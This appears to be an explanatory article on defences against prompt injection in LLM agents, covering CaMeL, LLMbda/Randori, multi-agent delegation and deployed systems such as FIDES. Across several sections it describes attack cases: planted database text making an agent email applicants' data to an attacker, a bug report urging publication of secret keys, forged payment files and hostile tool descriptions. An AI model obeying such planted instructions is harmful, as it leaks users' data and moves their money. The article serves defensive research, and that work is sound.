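AgentDojo suits CaMeL well, because only 6 of its 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan partway through. Li and colleagues wrote 60 tasks that all require this. In these tasks, outside text can also contain instructions the agent needs, such as a checkout page's instruction to log in first. CaMeL completed far fewer of these tasks than an undefended agent did.

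*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL with newer models on a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, in which a main agent delegates work to four specialists. CaMeL reduced the share of completed tasks by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures occurred because the program could not add a step after seeing a result. In other cases, a specialist returned data for the wrong machine or dates, and the program carried on because its author had not anticipated this mistake.

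Designers of such systems accept some of this loss. In *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025), Willison discusses a paper that recommends deliberately limiting agents so that they cannot solve arbitrary tasks.

These designs still protect against attackers who adapt. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested ten defences with planted text that a model rewrote after seeing which versions worked. The success rate of attacks on one filter, PIGuard, rose from zero to 28.0% with GPT-4o-mini. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it also reduced task completion the most on four of the five models.

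### What the LLMbda calculus proves

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes two leaks in CaMeL's label tracking. In a simplified version of the first example, a program sets a variable called `rich` to true, then changes it to false if the user's bank balance is low. CaMeL marks `rich` as secret only if the change happens. When the balance is high, `rich` stays public, so CaMeL lets the program email a stranger if `rich` is true. The stranger learns from the email that the balance is high.

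The second leak occurs because CaMeL retries programs that fail, and the retry code is outside the label tracking. Whether the policy blocks a program can depend on a secret, so each retry can reveal another bit of it. Peters-Gill and colleagues, who extended CaMeL's code, removed the retries but reported in October 2026 that their version still had the first leak.

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, to rule out such mistakes. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation with the model. If a secret determines whether a program adds to a public conversation, LLMbda stops the program.

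Their main theorem compares two runs of a program whose inputs differ only in data that some observer may not see. Let *P*₁(*x*) and *P*₂(*x*) be the probabilities that each run finishes with a result that looks like *x* to the observer. The theorem guarantees a function *Q*, whose values add up to at most 1, such that

*P*₁(*x*) ≤ *Q*(*x*) and *P*₂(*x*) ≤ *Q*(*x*) for every *x*.

If both runs always finish, *P*₁ and *P*₂ each add up to 1, so both must equal *Q*. The observer then sees the same probabilities in both cases and learns nothing about the hidden data. The same theorem shows that untrusted text cannot influence a result labelled as trusted.

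Some information can leak if a run may not finish, for example because a policy stops it. Half the sum of the differences |*P*₁(*x*) − *P*₂(*x*)| is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. If one run fails to finish 10% of the time and the other always finishes, half the sum is at most 0.05.

Garby and colleagues checked the proofs in the Lean proof assistant, and the theorems cover the same interpreter that calls the model. The guarantee holds even if an attacker controls everything the model writes, provided that developers label every source correctly and put a check on every sensitive tool. The proof also treats tools and data sources as part of the program, whereas a real bank or mail server is outside it.

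The program must also avoid "endorsement", a command that relabels untrusted data as trusted. Some tasks need it, such as paying a bill whose amount and recipient are in a file. Garby and colleagues proved that endorsement cannot expose secrets, but it lets untrusted data pass the trust checks.

### The price of enforcing the policies

Garby and colleagues used LLMbda to build an agent called Randori. It practises its program on made-up data until the program works, then runs it on the real data, so it needs no unsafe retries. They compared it with CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, each run three times. These are the results with GPT-5.2:

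| System | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| Randori, endorsement allowed | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |

The attack totals for CaMeL are lower because some runs did not finish. Banking is only one of AgentDojo's four groups of tasks, so the result with policies on does not contradict the earlier figure of 77%.

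In this benchmark, CaMeL's policies prevented hardly any attacks and kept many tasks from being completed, but there were few attacks left for them to prevent. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed an action that would not normally appear in the plan, so separating planning from reading was usually enough. One exception was a task that asked the agent to follow the instructions in a file. CaMeL's model wrote a program that could call any tool the file named, so whoever wrote the file could again control what the agent did.

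In both successful attacks on Randori, the user told the agent to pay whatever a file requested, and the attacker replaced the file with a false payment request. A label can show that the request came from a file, but not that it is false. Forbidding endorsement blocked these attacks, but it also prevented the agent from making genuine payments requested in a file.

Ma, Li and colleagues found that vague requests are generally riskier. With an undefended GPT-4o-mini, fixed attacks succeeded 87.5% of the time when the user left the choice of action to outside text, such as an online to-do list. The attacks succeeded less often when the user specified the action and all its details. Designs that derive permissions from the user's request resisted these attacks partly because they often gave the agent read-only access, which also prevented it from carrying out the tasks on the list.

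### When one agent instructs another

Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that several agents can be unsafe together even if each one uses CaMeL. In their example, a main agent asks a database agent for information about job applicants, summarises it, and asks a third agent to send the summary to Julie on Slack. An attacker has planted an instruction in the database. The first two agents treat it as data, but the main agent includes the summary in its request to the third agent, whose planning model reads the whole request as if it came from a trusted user. The third agent therefore also emails the applicants' information to the attacker.

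The fix is to send instructions and data separately. The main agent writes "Send the attached text to the recipient" as the instruction and passes the summary as a variable, which the third agent's planning model never reads. The interpreter rejects any instruction that contains text from a tool.

Peters-Gill and colleagues ran 949 attacks on each of five models in a multi-agent version of AgentDojo. On average, 12.9% succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and none with the separate channel. Most of the reduction came from older models. Without CaMeL, 36.1% of attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1, 1.5% against Fable 5, and none against GPT-5.5.

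A company that uses a strong model might therefore doubt that CaMeL's protection justifies completing fewer tasks. But these were fixed attacks, and Peters-Gill and colleagues cite a large public competition in which attackers fooled every leading model tested. Completing fewer tasks is easier to justify for an agent that can move money than for one that only drafts text.

### Where the labels and policies can be wrong

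A label is only as accurate as the rule that assigns it. Most of these systems trust whatever the user types, so if a user pastes in part of a stranger's email, any instructions in it become trusted. CaMeL's planning model also reads tool descriptions. Song, Dai and Tao (2026) point out in *Aligning Tool Descriptions and Implementations to Detect Prompt Injections in LLM Agents* that agents usually load these descriptions as trusted text, even when a stranger wrote the tool. A hostile tool server can therefore influence the plan.

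If the assistant saves a note from an untrusted document without the label marking it as untrusted, the note may affect a later request. *SPA* (2026) describes a system that keeps labels on saved results and hides their contents from the planning model.

Writing the policies also takes work, and users or administrators have to keep them up to date. One benchmark in *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) omits ROPE, a defence that tracks where sensitive arguments came from, because including it would have required new rules and tracking for 349 simulated environments. If a policy is too strict, it interrupts users so often that they may start approving everything.

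Even a correct policy protects only the call it checks, so these designs also need the policy checker and the tool to parse each call the same way. They do not check whether the answer itself is harmful or false. A user who asks for weapon instructions counts as a trusted source, so blocking that answer is left to an exchange classifier. Planted text can make a summary false without breaking any rule about where the summary may go.

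### What providers have deployed

OpenAI and Anthropic now limit which web addresses their tools can open. These limits are a form of least privilege, because they apply regardless of what the model writes.

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) announced that its Agent Framework, a kit for building agents, now includes an experimental information-flow system called FIDES. In the example, an agent reads a public bug report containing a planted instruction to publish a project's secret keys. The agent may open the file of keys, but doing so marks its whole context as private, so FIDES either blocks it from posting a public comment or asks a person first.

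By default, FIDES hides untrusted text from the main model and has a quarantined model read it. This requires a second model call, and the main model works from a summary. If a developer turns this default off, one untrusted document makes the rest of the run untrusted, which can block legitimate work. Microsoft says the checks slow each tool call but gives no measurements. FIDES also treats data from any unlabeled tool as trusted and public, so a developer who forgets one label can leave a gap without seeing an error.

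GitHub's MCP server can now label its results as untrusted if they come from public projects and trusted if they come from private ones. Instructions planted by someone with access to a private project would therefore be labeled trusted. GitHub's Copilot CLI, a coding agent, can enforce policies based on these labels if the user turns on an experimental setting. The setting covers only some of the GitHub server's tools and does not yet support other MCP servers.
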